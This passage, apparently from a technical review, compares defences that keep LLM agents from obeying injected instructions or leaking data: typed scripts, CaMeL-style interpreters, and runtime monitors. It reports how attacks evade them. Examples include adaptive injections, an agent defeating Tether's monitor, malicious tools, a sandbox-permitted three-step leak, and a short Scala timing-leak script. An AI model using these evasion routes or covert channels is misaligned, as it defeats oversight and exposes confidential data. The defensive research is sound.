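Other groups have since run CaMeL on AgentDojo with their own set-ups. *SecureClaw* (2026) adapted CaMeL's published code and ran it on a version of the benchmark with 97 user tasks and 629 attack trials. None of the attacks succeeded. CaMeL completed 29.9% of the tasks when it was not under attack and 31.0% when it was, whereas the SecureClaw system completed about 61%. These results confirm CaMeL's security, but its utility was far lower than with o4-mini-high. Differences in the model and in the adapted code could explain part of the gap.

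CaMeL's effect on utility varies widely between models, so a result for one model is a poor guide to its effect on another. On AssetOpsBench, *Can CaMeLs Talk?* found that GPT-5.5 completed 87.5% of tasks without CaMeL and 82.1% with it. Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite, a much weaker model, fell from 64.3% to 20.5%. More capable models tended to lose less, but Claude Fable 5 was an exception, falling from 88.4% to 67.0%.

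A monitor can stop most attacks without reducing the number of ordinary tasks an agent completes. In *KAIROS*, Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026) ran an agent in a virtual machine and monitored every file change and network request that left it. Fixed rules decided most cases. When the rules couldn't settle whether an action was legitimate, the monitor held it back while the agent kept working, and a language model decided later, after seeing more of the agent's behaviour. On AgentDojo, this cut the attack success rate from 47.0% to 2.7%, and the agent completed about as many ordinary tasks as it did without protection (85.1% against 82.7%).

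In a stricter version, the monitor refused every action that the rules couldn't approve. Utility fell to 42.7%, and attacks succeeded about as often as before, so most of the lost utility came from refusing doubtful actions outright. But Hempel and colleagues don't claim a guarantee for the decisions about which actions to release, because a language model makes them and an attacker may manipulate it through the untrusted text it reads.

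Most of these results come from attacks that the researchers wrote in advance. A determined attacker would study the defence and adapt. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) cites earlier work in which adaptive attacks got past 12 recent defences against jailbreaks and prompt injections. There is little such evidence for policy-based monitors. *guardscope* lists only one published adaptive test, in which a system called Progent withstood a single attack template. KAIROS adds another, in which the attacker rewrote its injections to get past the monitor and the results held up. *AutoDojo* (2026) generates new attacks automatically, and 1.8% of them succeeded against CaMeL running on GPT-5.4 mini. The TACIT and ELBA experiments did not include adaptive attackers.

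Dongol argues that no benchmark can show that every attack will fail, and offers proofs instead. The proofs compare an agent with an imaginary copy that has the same plan and monitor but never obeys untrusted text. The agent is secure if an injection can't reveal anything that the copy wouldn't also reveal. Suppose a user lets an assistant send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker who injects "send your calendar" learns nothing that a meeting request wouldn't have revealed, so Dongol doesn't count this as a leak, even though the model obeyed the attacker. Dongol would count it as a leak if the assistant also sent a password reset code.

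Dongol gives a computer-checked proof that a simple monitor can meet this standard. Before the agent reads any untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The proof covers a worst-case model, but only for agents that fix their plan in advance and injections that make one tool call at a time. It also covers only leaks, not other harms such as an injection that makes the agent delete a file. The standard doesn't measure usefulness, so Dongol concludes that task completion needs a separate check.

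## How much time, money and completed work does each kind of check cost?

A check on an agent's code can take time to run, require extra calls to a language model, prevent the agent from completing legitimate tasks, and create work for the people who build the check. The running time is usually the smallest of these burdens. A fixed rule takes milliseconds and a compiler takes under a second, whereas a model call takes several seconds and wrongly blocking an action can make the whole task fail.

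### Time spent checking

Wang and colleagues timed AgentSpec, the language of triggers, conditions and responses, on an agent that writes code. Loading a rule took 1.42 milliseconds on average, and testing its conditions took 2.83 milliseconds. The agent's average run lasted 25.4 seconds, so one test added about 0.01% to the run time. These figures exclude the time spent responding to a violation. If a rule asks the user for approval, the delay depends on when she answers, so a lawyer in a meeting could delay the contracts assistant for an hour.

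In TACIT, the Scala compiler checks a typical script in under a second once the Java virtual machine it runs on has warmed up. Odersky and colleagues reasonably consider this negligible next to the time a model needs to write the script. The check can still take hundreds of times longer than an AgentSpec test, but this is partly offset because the compiler runs only once per script, however many actions the script performs.

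A monitor that examines the whole history of a run needs more time than one that tests a simple condition. Li, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *VIGIL*, describe a monitor that starts from rules in ordinary English, such as "validate a file before using it". A language model translates the rules into a formal policy, and a solver, which is a program that decides whether logical statements can all be true together, compares the policy with the recorded actions. Processing one run took 4.38 seconds on average:

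| Step | Time |
|---|---|
| Turn the tool calls into a uniform record | 0.06 s |
| Translate the rules with one model call | 4.05 s |
| Check the record with the solver | 0.27 s |

The total stayed about the same for longer runs. The model's input is a list of the tools, argument names and file types that the run has used, and this list soon stops growing.

Li and colleagues call the enforcement "effectively free" because a company can store the translated policy and reuse it. This is somewhat optimistic, since the 0.27 seconds covers one pass over a finished run, while a live monitor has to check again before each action. Also, when translating a policy, the model can use only names that have already appeared in the run, so a stored policy may need another translation when the agent first uses a new tool.

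### Model calls to rewrite rejected code

Every retry after a compiler error requires another model call. Odersky and colleagues counted these retries on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles requests from simulated customers. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of scripts needed a retry, depending on the model and the kind of customer service. DeepSeek V3.2 had the highest rate, on airline tasks, while the other two models stayed below 1.6%. Scripts that needed a retry took 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average.

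LACUNA, the related system in which a model fills gaps in a running program, had more rejections. Zhao and colleagues tested it on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of hard research questions about a fixed collection of documents. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the code that DeepSeek V4 Flash generated, and two-thirds of the questions needed no retry. On the retail tasks in τ²-bench, it rejected 22.4% of the same model's code. For a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, it rejected only 3.2% of the code on retail tasks but 89% on telecom tasks.

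Suppose the compiler rejects a share *q* of attempts, and a retry is as likely to fail as a first attempt. An accepted script then takes 1/(1 − *q*) attempts on average, and the chance that three attempts all fail is *q*³.

| Rejection rate | Average attempts per accepted script | Chance that three attempts all fail |
|---|---|---|
| 8.6% | 1.09 | 0.06% |
| 22.4% | 1.29 | 1.1% |
| 89% | 9.1 | 70% |

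Real attempts aren't independent, because the compiler's error message can help the model correct its code, while a script that is hard to write correctly is likely to fail more than once. The table still suggests that retries add modest overhead for a competent model and can leave a weak one completing almost no work. The policy is enforced in both cases, because rejected code never runs.

In ELBA, the Haskell system, retries took only 3.4% of the running time in AgentDojo's Slack tasks. Zhou and colleagues counted 0.13 retries per run on average, and only 7 of 2,688 runs used up all their retries. ELBA still took about three times as long as CaMeL to finish the benchmark, mainly because an ELBA agent calls the model again after reading data, while CaMeL keeps to its fixed plan.

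The running time therefore triples because the agent can adapt, and an untyped agent that worked the same way would take most of that extra time too. CaMeL is faster because it is less flexible. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL completed none of the open-ended tasks in AgentDyn, another benchmark for agents under attack.

Typed agents can also make fewer model calls than untyped ones. In Zhou and colleagues' citation test, the untyped agent made about four times as many model calls as ELBA and used 65 times as many input tokens, the pieces of text that AI companies charge for. Most of this saving probably comes from ELBA's use of scripts, which keep bulk data out of the model's input, rather than from types.

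### Model calls to judge actions

Some monitors call a model to decide whether an action is acceptable. AgentBouncer makes about eight such calls in an average task, and Joos and Pradel report that it adds 47 seconds and $0.0036 to a task without attacks. For a company that runs 1,000 such tasks a day, AgentBouncer would add $3.60 to the daily bill but about 13 hours to the agents' total working time.

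Joos and Pradel compared AgentBouncer with AgentSentinel, a monitor that inspects events after they happen and stops the program if one looks harmful. AgentSentinel added about three and a half minutes and three and a half cents per task, which was 4.5 times as much time and 9.6 times as much money as AgentBouncer added.

Agent-Sentry reduces calls to a language model by running two cheaper checks first. Before an agent sends or changes anything, a classifier compares the sequence of actions, and the sources of the values in them, with earlier legitimate runs. It then allows the action, blocks it or marks it as unclear. The second check allows an unclear action if its sensitive values, such as email addresses, are on an approved list and came from a trusted source. A language model reviews only the unclear actions that the second check doesn't allow.

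### The delay in a task of 50 actions

Suppose an agent performs 50 actions. If each rule check takes *r* seconds, each model call takes *m* seconds, and the monitor refers *k* of the actions to a model, the total delay is

50*r* + *km*.

AgentSpec's 2.83 milliseconds is a reasonable value for *r*. VIGIL's translation call takes 4.05 seconds, which is an acceptable value for *m*, although a judge with a short prompt might answer faster. The table also includes, for comparison, a solver like VIGIL's and a compiler that checks ten scripts of five actions each.

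| Kind of check | Calculation | Total delay |
|---|---|---|
| A fixed rule on every action | 50 × 0.00283 s | 0.14 s |
| A compiler on ten scripts | 10 × under 1 s | under 10 s |
| A solver on every action, after one translation | 4.05 s + 50 × 0.27 s | 17.6 s |
| A fixed rule on every action and a model judge on five | 0.14 s + 5 × 4.05 s | 20.4 s |
| A model judge on every action | 50 × 4.05 s | 202.5 s |

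The solver's figure is probably too high, since most of its checks would cover only part of the run. The compiler's figure leaves out retries. At the highest rate in the TACIT tests, ten scripts would need about one retry in total, which would add five or six seconds.

If the agent's own model also takes about four seconds to write each of the ten scripts, writing them takes about 40 seconds. A fixed rule adds no noticeable time, but a judge on every action makes the task about six times as long. If the agent instead calls its tools one at a time, it already needs about 200 seconds of model time, and the judge only doubles that. Scripts save time by reducing the number of model calls, and a judge on every action cancels that saving.

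A monitor doesn't always have to make the agent wait. KAIROS holds doubtful actions and judges them while the agent keeps working, which saves time unless the agent needs the result of one of those actions.

### Ordinary tasks that the agent no longer completes

Typed scripts could reduce an agent's success rate if they are hard for the model to write. The two Scala systems gave opposite results on τ²-bench. The table shows the share of tasks agents completed with ordinary tool calls and with typed code.

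| System and model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, typed code | Retail, tool calls | Retail, typed code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT, gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| TACIT, MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| TACIT, DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| LACUNA, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 75.5% | 70.0% | 80.9% | 58.8% |
| LACUNA, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 56.0% | 38.0% | 52.6% | 43.9% |

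Every model did slightly better with TACIT than with tool calls. Odersky and colleagues credit the compiler's error messages and the typed results, which specify exactly what a tool returns. But on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with tool calls, a difference of five problems, which is too small to mean much.

LACUNA did worse than tool calls in all four airline and retail comparisons. Over all 392 tasks, which also include telecom support, DeepSeek V4 Flash completed 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with tool calls. That is a difference of about 55 tasks, although Zhao and colleagues describe these results as "on par".

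Rejected code doesn't fully explain the loss. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite lost almost nine points on retail tasks, where the compiler rejected only 3.2% of its code. In one set of telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of its code, but it solved nearly as many tasks with LACUNA (14.9%) as with tool calls (15.8%), though it failed most of them either way. LACUNA also gives the model more to do than TACIT, since the code it writes controls when to call the model again and what to keep for later.

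None of these tests compares typed scripts with untyped scripts, so they can't separate the effect of types from the effect of acting through code. The BrowseComp-Plus test has no comparison. LACUNA answered 27.1% of its questions correctly with DeepSeek V4 Flash, and Zhao and colleagues conclude that type checking doesn't reduce accuracy, but they didn't run an untyped agent on the same questions.

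Monitors lose tasks mainly by blocking legitimate actions:

- AgentSpec reduced the share of safe household tasks that a simulated robot completed from 58.62% to 54.26%.
- VIGIL raised a false alarm on 8 of 80 harmless runs. In one case, the original rule restricted *bulk* changes to a calendar, but the model dropped the word "bulk" when it translated the rule, so VIGIL objected when the agent moved a single meeting.
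- Progent, which permits only calls on an approved list, blocked something in 47 of the same 80 runs when Li and colleagues tested it. Their policies rarely listed every safe command.
- Agent-Sentry allowed 95.1% of harmless runs on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, so it interrupted about one in 20.

AgentBouncer's failure rate on harmless tool calls was 0.25%. If failures were independent, the chance of at least one in a task of 50 calls would be 1 − 0.9975⁵⁰, or about 12%. Yet the agent solved 72.94% of its programming tasks with AgentBouncer and 71.47% without it. The difference is too small to suggest that monitoring helped, but the similar rates suggest that the agent could usually work around a failed call.

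Agents don't always recover so well from a blocked action. Research on the "verifier tax", the completed work that an agent loses to checking, found that checks blocked up to 94% of unsafe actions but few tasks ended both safe and complete. Blocking an action leaves the task unfinished. For example, if a monitor stops the contracts assistant from emailing a stranger, the lawyer still has no summary. The agent still needs to find a permitted way to finish the task, but it may repeat the blocked action or give up instead.

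A script that a compiler rejects likewise does no harm and no work. The blocking rate is therefore a poor measure of how useful a check is. The share of all tasks completed safely is a better measure because it also falls when a policy is too strict, as it did when ELBA agents failed to complete tasks because of their own policies.

### The work of building the checks

TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines of Scala and contains the capabilities, the `Classified` wrapper and the connection to the trusted model. Each new set of tools also needs typed definitions. The definitions for the airline and retail tasks are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the JSON descriptions they replaced. Odersky and colleagues point out that only the reusable library requires an expert in capture checking. An agent can help write the definitions for a new set of tools, and a person can review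 them before the agent starts work.

Rules for a monitor can be much shorter. The two AgentSpec rules for the law firm take ten lines, plus a small Python function for each condition. Wang and colleagues covered 750 risky coding scenarios with 25 handwritten rules, and 250 household scenarios with 12. One rule about pouring liquids prevented 96 of the household hazards. But the law firm's rules limit only the number of emails and their recipients, whereas TACIT's library also controls what happens to the contract text.

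Developers can have a model write the rules, but somebody then has to find the mistakes. The AgentSpec rules that OpenAI's o1 model wrote for the coding agent caught 87.26% of the risky code. Some rules recognised only the sensitive files named in the examples given to o1 and missed similar ones.

VIGIL and Agent-Sentry are designed to avoid handwritten rules. VIGIL's own program is about 7,000 lines of Python, which isn't directly comparable with TACIT's 1,000 lines because TACIT also relies on the whole Scala compiler. VIGIL needs no new code for each set of tools, only a description of the rules in English. Agent-Sentry learns what is normal from records of legitimate runs, so a firm that has just installed a new assistant would have to collect or simulate those records first.

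For the law firm, checking a few rules when the assistant calls a tool would be the cheapest way to enforce requirements A (file access) and C (the number of emails). The typed library becomes better value if several assistants share it or if the firm needs its protection for confidential text.

### Does "no monitoring overhead" matter?

Odersky and colleagues list the lack of monitoring overhead as one advantage of types. For checks on tool calls, the advantage is very small. The contracts script performs about five actions, so replacing AgentSpec's tests with types would save about 14 milliseconds, but the compiler could take up to a second. For these checks, types compare well only with monitors that call a model or a solver.

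Static types have a much greater advantage when a runtime check would have to run inside the program's own calculations. Research on gradual typing has measured how much such checks can slow a program. A gradually typed language lets a programmer add types to some parts of a program and leave the rest untyped. To guarantee that those types hold, the language checks values when they pass from an untyped part to a typed one. A number needs one quick check, but a list may need one for every element. A function needs a wrapper that checks each later call, and a function that crosses the boundary repeatedly can collect several wrappers.

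In *Is Sound Gradual Typing Dead?* (2016), Takikawa, Feltey and colleagues measured how much runtime checks at the boundaries between typed and untyped code slow down programs in the language Typed Racket. Each module can be typed or untyped, so a program with *n* modules has 2ⁿ versions, and they compared the running times of these versions. Some partly typed versions ran more than 100 times slower than the untyped program, although most fully typed versions ran at about the original speed. The slowdown came from the number of boundary checks.

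Better compilers can remove much of this overhead. In *Sound Gradual Typing: Only Mostly Dead* (2017), Bauman, Bolz-Tereick and colleagues used an experimental compiler that optimises a program while it runs. It eliminated more than 90% of the overhead on typical benchmarks.

The number of checks matters for agents too. If a script examined a million words in a folder of contracts and a monitor spent 2.83 milliseconds on each, the monitoring would take 47 minutes. AgentBouncer's 28,000 decisions per task add only 47 seconds because nearly all come from fixed rules or earlier verdicts. Sending all of them to a model, at 4.05 seconds each, would take more than 31 hours.

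TACIT avoids this problem for confidential text. The compiler checks once that the function passed to `map` is pure, and the function can then process a million words without further security checks. A monitor that tracks labels must update them as the script computes new values. Updating a label can be far quicker than testing an AgentSpec rule, but the total time still grows with the amount of computation. LIO reduces that time by using a single label for the whole computation.

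## Which actions and channels does each kind of check miss?

A check's coverage is the share of relevant effects that pass through it, where an effect is relevant if the policy could forbid it. Suppose some of the law firm's contracts arrive as PDF files, and the assistant's script starts a separate program to convert them to text. The converter opens a contract, writes a temporary copy and contacts its maker's website to look for updates. A check on the script covers the start of the converter but misses the other three effects, so its coverage is one in four. Coverage is only a rough guide, since a single missed effect can leak the contract.

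### Code outside the typed language

TACIT's compiler checks Scala code, but a PDF converter is usually an existing program written in another language. A script can start such a program through `requestExecPermission`, which takes a list of permitted commands. The types control which code may start the converter but not what the converter does afterwards. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that the static guarantee is then only as good as the list. If the converter posted contracts to a website, the script would still type-check. If the converter returned its output as an ordinary string, the contract text would lose its `Classified` wrapper.

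They advise permitting only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` or `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. `sbt` shows why the sandbox matters. It builds Scala projects and runs code it finds in them, so it is only as safe as that code.

The local model behind `summarise` is also outside the typed language. The types prevent a script from using it to send anything, but they can't ensure that it retains no data between requests. If it retained a contract, a later script could send it an ordinary prompt and get contract text back as an ordinary string. Odersky and colleagues leave it to whoever sets up the model to prevent this.

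Many agents also come with a built-in tool for shell commands, and those commands don't go through TACIT's compiler. The firm would have to remove that tool or confine it separately. ELBA has less of this problem because the whole application is in Haskell, but a Haskell program that starts a converter has no more control over the converter than a Scala script does.

### What time and failure reveal

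The following script satisfies TACIT's types. The function `countTo` counts up to a number and returns it, so it is pure.

```
text.map(t => if t.contains("penalty") then countTo(5000000000L) else 0L)
println("Done.")
```

The script prints the same word whatever the contract contains, but it takes a few seconds longer if there is a penalty clause. The company that hosts the assistant's model can measure the delay and learn whether the clause is there. If the script instead looped forever when it found the clause, the company could learn the same thing from whether the script terminates.

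Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee, and give the example of an agent that leaks a single bit this way. An agent could leak more by running many scripts. At eight bits per character, a 20-character password takes 160 single-bit leaks, and a 30,000-character contract takes 240,000. The leak is therefore a realistic threat to passwords and keys, but much less so to long documents.

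Monitoring has the same gap. Costa and colleagues leave timing and the length of network packets out of their model of Fides, so an outsider could learn private information from either. A runtime could slow the timing leak by returning results only at fixed times, but every task would then take longer.

An exception's error message could include contract text, but exceptions are easier to control. TACIT turns them into ordinary values by having functions return a `Try`, a standard Scala type that holds either a result or a failure. The library can wrap the failure so that the script can't find out that something went wrong. The same method covers early exits from a loop or function, which Scala 3 implements as exceptions. The compiler also prevents a script from storing a capability inside an exception, because the exception could carry file access out of its block. But `Try` is designed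 not to catch the most serious errors, such as running out of memory, so the surrounding runtime has to hide those.

### Missing information and missing computing power

Hamlen and colleagues distinguish two reasons a mechanism may fail to enforce a policy. It may be unable to observe a relevant event, in which case every other mechanism with the same information fails too. Or it may have the information but lack the computing power to reach a decision, in which case a different mechanism, such as a better judge, might succeed.

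Several failures in Joos and Pradel's tests happened because the monitor lacked information. AgentSentinel, which inspects events after they happen, doesn't record when one process kills another, and 16 of 20 attacks that did this succeeded. AgentBouncer showed its model that a program was trying to write to the user's shell settings but not the text it would write, and 5 of 20 such attacks succeeded. Joos and Pradel suggest showing the model that text as well.

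A monitor with enough information to identify an attack can still do so too late. In 24 attacks, AgentSentinel killed the process only after the attack had taken full effect.

### Tool calls, interpreters and system calls

A tool-call monitor receives each tool's name, arguments and result. In one of Joos and Pradel's attacks, a tool called `validate_patch` checks a proposed code change, as advertised, but also secretly deletes a system file. Both the call and the result look normal. Joos and Pradel ran 85 attacks with malicious tools like this one and 255 of other kinds, such as prompt injections and scripts planted in the project.

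| Monitor | What it checks | Malicious tools that succeeded | All attacks that succeeded | Harmless tool calls that failed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| none | nothing | 100% | 99.41% | – |
| Drift | tool calls, against a model's plan | 100% | 83.53% | 1.04% |
| AgentSpec | tool calls, against fixed rules | 89.41% | 28.82% | 25.87% |
| LlamaGuard | tool calls, with a trained classifier | 12.94% | 11.47% | 71.57% |
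| AgentSentinel | system events, afterwards | 50.59% | 33.82% | 2.48% |
| AgentBouncer | system calls, beforehand | 7.06% | 10.59% | 0.25% |

The last column comes from runs without attacks. LlamaGuard stopped nearly as many attacks as AgentBouncer, but only by refusing most calls of any kind, and the agent completed 1.18% of its programming tasks. AgentSpec stopped a few malicious tools only because its other refusals kept the agent from reaching them. Joos and Pradel designed both AgentBouncer and the attack set, so the exact ranking deserves some caution. It is more certain that tool-call monitors fail against malicious tools, because the call doesn't contain the information they need.

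An interpreter such as CaMeL's provides more information about the script but no more about the tools. It executes every line of the script itself, so it can track contract text from one variable to another, but it treats the PDF converter as a single call. Tracking the script this closely also restricts how it can be written. According to Odersky and colleagues, CaMeL's plans can't define their own functions or use recursion.

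A system-call monitor, by contrast, covers every program that the script starts, in any language, but has no record of the variables inside them. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) presents a monitor of this kind that runs each command on a disposable copy of the file system and keeps the changes only if the policy permits them. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats this as a flow of data between them. This avoids missing real flows but creates false alarms. For example, a command that searches a whole folder opens every file in it, so Tether treats the agent as having read any secrets there. Such reads caused 17 of Tether's 74 false alarms.

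System calls also reveal little about network traffic. Joos and Pradel point out that installing a package and stealing a file can both appear as an encrypted connection to some address. AgentBouncer gets the missing details from its proxy. AgentSentinel, which lacks those details, classified the attacker's connection as safe in 32 of 100 network attacks, while AgentBouncer did so in 2.

For the script that converts PDFs, the three kinds of monitor would receive the following:

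| Event | Tool-call monitor | Interpreter | System-call monitor |
|---|---|---|---|
| The script copies contract text to another variable | no | yes | no |
| The script calls a tool that starts the converter | yes | yes | only the start of the converter |
| The converter opens a file | no | no | yes |
| The converter contacts a website | no | no | the address, or the whole request with a proxy |

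Tether blocked all 344 attacks in its main test and raised false alarms on 4.7% of 1,590 harmless runs, but the test included only runs in which Tether could trace and model every action. It left out background processes, because Tether stops tracing when the main command ends, and databases, because queries go to a server that is already running.

Sistla and colleagues then examined the other runs they could replay. Tether could often block a background process or a database connection without knowing its purpose. But 28.2% of the runs on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other depended on the meaning of content, and they say no formal monitor can judge that meaning. Their example is a malicious change to a file the agent is allowed to edit. A type checker for permissions would also miss this change, because the edit has the correct type.

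Rules that match the text of a shell command are an unreliable substitute for any of these checks, as Zhou and colleagues argue.

### Why a sandbox can allow both steps of a leak

Sistla and colleagues describe an agent that may read a confidential inventory and may upload a status report to GitHub, a website for sharing code. It takes three steps:

1. It uploads the report, which is harmless.
2. It copies the inventory over the report.
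3. It uploads the report again, with exactly the same command as in step 1.

A sandbox that lets the agent do its job has to permit reading the inventory, writing the report and connecting to GitHub, and the leak needs only those permissions. No rule that applies to each command alone can allow step 1 and block step 3, because the commands are identical. Tether can distinguish them because it keeps a label on each file. The copy in step 2 changes the report's label from public to sensitive, so Tether blocks the second upload. It would also block the upload if the agent had first passed the inventory through several temporary files.

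Email has the same problem. *Operationalizing CaMeL* notes that if a sandbox permits outgoing mail, an injected prompt can still make the agent send secrets in a plausible message.

A sandbox is much more effective when a program needs only one of the two permissions. The PDF converter has to read contracts but doesn't need the internet, so the firm can run it in a sandbox with no network connection. The converter then can't send the contracts anywhere, whatever its code does. The compiler can't provide that protection. Odersky and colleagues also recommend a sandbox in case a script escapes through a bug in the Java virtual machine, which runs the compiled code.

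### When labelled text enters a conversation

Systems like CaMeL attach labels to values inside a program. Odersky and colleagues argue that these labels get lost in conversation. Once a script prints a contract and the text enters the model's input, the text no longer carries a label, and the model can copy it into a later script as a new, unlabeled string.

TACIT avoids this because the model receives only a placeholder when a script prints confidential text. The protection continues across turns. If the user asks a follow-up question about a summary, the next script can print `summary.map(_.length)`, and the user sees the length while the model again receives only the placeholder.

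The criticism doesn't apply to all label tracking. Fides labels the conversation too, and whatever the model writes inherits that label. If a summary that only the lawyer and her partner may read entered the conversation, Fides would restrict a copy the model retyped to the same two readers. Tether also keeps a label for everything the agent has read. These systems keep the protection but lose precision, because a harmless message written later in the same conversation gets the same restriction. Costa and colleagues cite a method that recovers some of the precision. It works out which earlier messages influenced an answer, generates the answer again from those messages alone, and gives it only their labels.

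TACIT's approach is still better for the law firm if the company hosting the model isn't allowed to read the contracts, since labeling the conversation doesn't help once the company has the text. But neither system protects text that the lawyer enters herself. If she copies a sentence from the summary on her screen into her next request, TACIT passes it to the hosted model as plain text. Fides normally labels users' messages as public, so it wouldn't restrict the sentence either.

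### Comparing the trusted bases

TACIT depends on the Scala compiler, which is far too large for people to analyse and test completely, as Anderson's condition requires. It also depends on every library function that a person has marked as safe. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache, which stores the results of a pure function in a hidden variable to avoid computing them twice. The compiler can't approve the variable, so a reviewer has to establish that it only ever holds earlier results.

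CaMeL instead relies on a custom interpreter, which is more specialised than a general compiler but has fewer users to find its faults. ELBA reuses LIO so that its developers don't have to trust a new label tracker, and Zhou and colleagues point to formal proofs of LIO's soundness. The developers still have to trust the Haskell compiler.

Tether's trusted base includes the operating system's core, the tracing tool, the network proxy and the code that translates system calls into actions such as "copy" or "upload". Sistla and colleagues have computer-checked proofs that their policy satisfies seven security properties, such as never sending secret data to an outside host. But the proofs are about the translated actions, so they don't help if the translation is wrong. The translation was wrong in an early version, and an AI agent told to get past the monitor succeeded in 40% of attempts. One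 gap involved hard links, which give a single file several names. After the researchers fixed the faults they found, the rate fell to zero.

Nada Amin and Ross Tate showed in 2016 that the type systems of both Java and Scala were unsound. Without using a cast, a program could make the compiler accept a value of one type as a value of an unrelated type. Their examples used `null`, a value that means "no object" and that both languages accepted in place of any object. Scala 3 has since added an option called explicit nulls, which allows `null` only where a type permits it, and safe mode always turns this option on. Explicit nulls block the original Scala example, though a null can still appear if a program reads a field before setting it.

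A similar fault in capture checking would be harder to notice. When a program treats a number as a string, the Java virtual machine usually stops it with an error. But capture sets exist only during compilation, so if a fault let a script pass off an email-sending function as pure, the virtual machine would run it without an error.

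## Can checks be reused and combined without re-examining the whole system?

Static checks are easy to combine because they can only accept or reject a program. If a script has to pass two of them, the order makes no difference. Monitors that change a program's actions are harder to combine, because one monitor's change can affect another's decision. However, a firm can often add a rule to a monitor without changing the agent, whereas a new rule expressed in types can require changes to existing code.

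### Joining two contract tools

Suppose the lawyer wants a summary of what changed between last year's contract and this year's. Odersky and colleagues describe a similar task, with one tool that compares two texts and another that summarises the differences. In simplified form, the tools have these signatures:

```
def diff(earlier: String, later: String): String
def summarise(text: Classified[String]): Classified[String]
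```

The assistant joins them in three lines:

```
val pair    = lastYear.aggregate(thisYear)
val changes = pair.map((a, b) => diff(a, b))
val report  = summarise(changes)
```

The compiler checks them in order:

1. `aggregate` combines two wrapped texts into one wrapped pair.
2. `map` requires a pure function. A global Scala object that uses a global capability has to list it in a `uses` clause, and the object containing `diff` has no such clause. A function that only calls `diff` is therefore pure.
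3. `map` returns a `Classified[String]`, which is the type that `summarise` accepts.

The compiler needs only the signatures of the two tools to do this, not their bodies. It checked each body against its signature when the firm compiled the library, and it relies on that result for every later script. This is called modular checking. A firm with 20 tools needs only 20 body checks, although a script could join those tools in 380 ordered pairs and many more longer chains.

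The firm can also replace a function's body. If it makes `diff` faster, it doesn't have to recheck any scripts. If it makes `diff` send both texts to an online comparison service, the object has to declare a network capability, and the `map` line no longer compiles. Zhao and colleagues show that a function for reviewing a code change can keep the same signature whether its body is a single call to a model, ordinary code, or a mixture of the two.

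Without signatures of this kind, safety often depends on facts about the whole program. In the Google technical report *Safe Coding*, Kern (2025) traces many persistent vulnerabilities to such facts, which a single developer can't reliably reason about in a large system.

A type signature helps only with the properties it records. If one tool returns a contract as a plain string and another emails any plain string, each could pass its own review, but a script that joined them would leak the contract. TACIT prevents this leak only because its library wraps the text when a script reads it.

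### Do annotations avoid an exponential cost?

Odersky and colleagues argue that if CaMeL allowed user-defined functions, giving modular guarantees before the program runs would require an analysis of the whole program that takes a lot of computation.

The difficulty comes from passing functions as values. When a checker with no annotations to rely on reaches `map(f)`, it has to determine which functions `f` could be. The answer depends on which data can reach that line, which depends on which functions ran earlier. Control-flow analysis works out both together.

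The analysis's precision depends on how well it separates different uses of the same function. Suppose a script calls `clean` on a contract and then on a public title. An analysis that merges the two calls treats both results as possibly containing contract text, so it would reject an email containing only the cleaned title. A method called kCFA separates uses of a function by the last *k* calls that led to them, and *k* = 1 is enough here.

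*Deciding kCFA is complete for EXPTIME* (Van Horn and Mairson, 2013) proves that for every *k* above 0, any algorithm for kCFA needs exponential time in the worst case. *Resolving and Exploiting the k-CFA Paradox* (Might, Smaragdakis and Van Horn, 2013) explains why. If a function uses *n* variables from the surrounding code, and each could have received its value in either of two calls, the analysis may have to consider 2ⁿ combinations, which is more than a billion for 30 variables.

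Capture sets make this search unnecessary. The parameter of `map` has an empty capture set, so the compiler has to check each function only where a script passes it to `map`.

Odersky and colleagues' argument is a good one for annotations over static analysis without them, but it is weak against tracking labels at run time. kCFA estimates which values could reach a line, whereas a run-time tracker has the actual value and its label, and the tracker's work grows with the number of steps the script executes. In ELBA, the LIO library tracks labels at run time in Haskell, where scripts can define recursive functions and pass functions as values, so CaMeL's restriction comes from its own design rather than from run-time tracking in general. The argument applies only to guarantees given before the run, which CaMeL doesn't offer.

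The complexity result could matter for a hybrid monitor, which also analyses the branches that a script skips. If a skipped branch would have called a function it received from another function, the monitor may have to work out which functions that could be.

Even static analysis can avoid exponential running time. The simplest version of kCFA, with *k* = 0, takes polynomial time. Might and colleagues show that kCFA also takes polynomial time on object-oriented programs, because these copy the variables they need into an object all at once. They use the same idea to design a polynomial-time analysis for functional programs, with some loss of precision. A bad worst case can also be harmless in practice. Van Horn and Mairson point out that type inference for the language ML has an exponential worst case too, and programmers use it happily, though they add that flow analysis has been slow in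 practice.

So an analyser without annotations could probably handle an agent's short scripts. But if someone changed a library function, the analyser might have to re-analyse every program that used the function. Signatures avoid that work, even when the analysis is fast.

### Passing permissions to sub-agents

An agent can give part of its task to a sub-agent, which is another model call with its own prompt. In ELBA and LACUNA, the parent agent's script calls the sub-agent like any other function, so the type checker applies the parent's limits to the sub-agent.

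In ELBA's bibliography example, the parent's script has the type `BibIO ()`. A sub-agent that runs as a step in that script is limited to the same `BibIO` operations. The parent can restrict the sub-agent further, for example by asking for an `Int`, which rules out every side effect. It can't ask for a sub-agent of type `IO ()`, for the same reason that it can't call `writeFile` itself.

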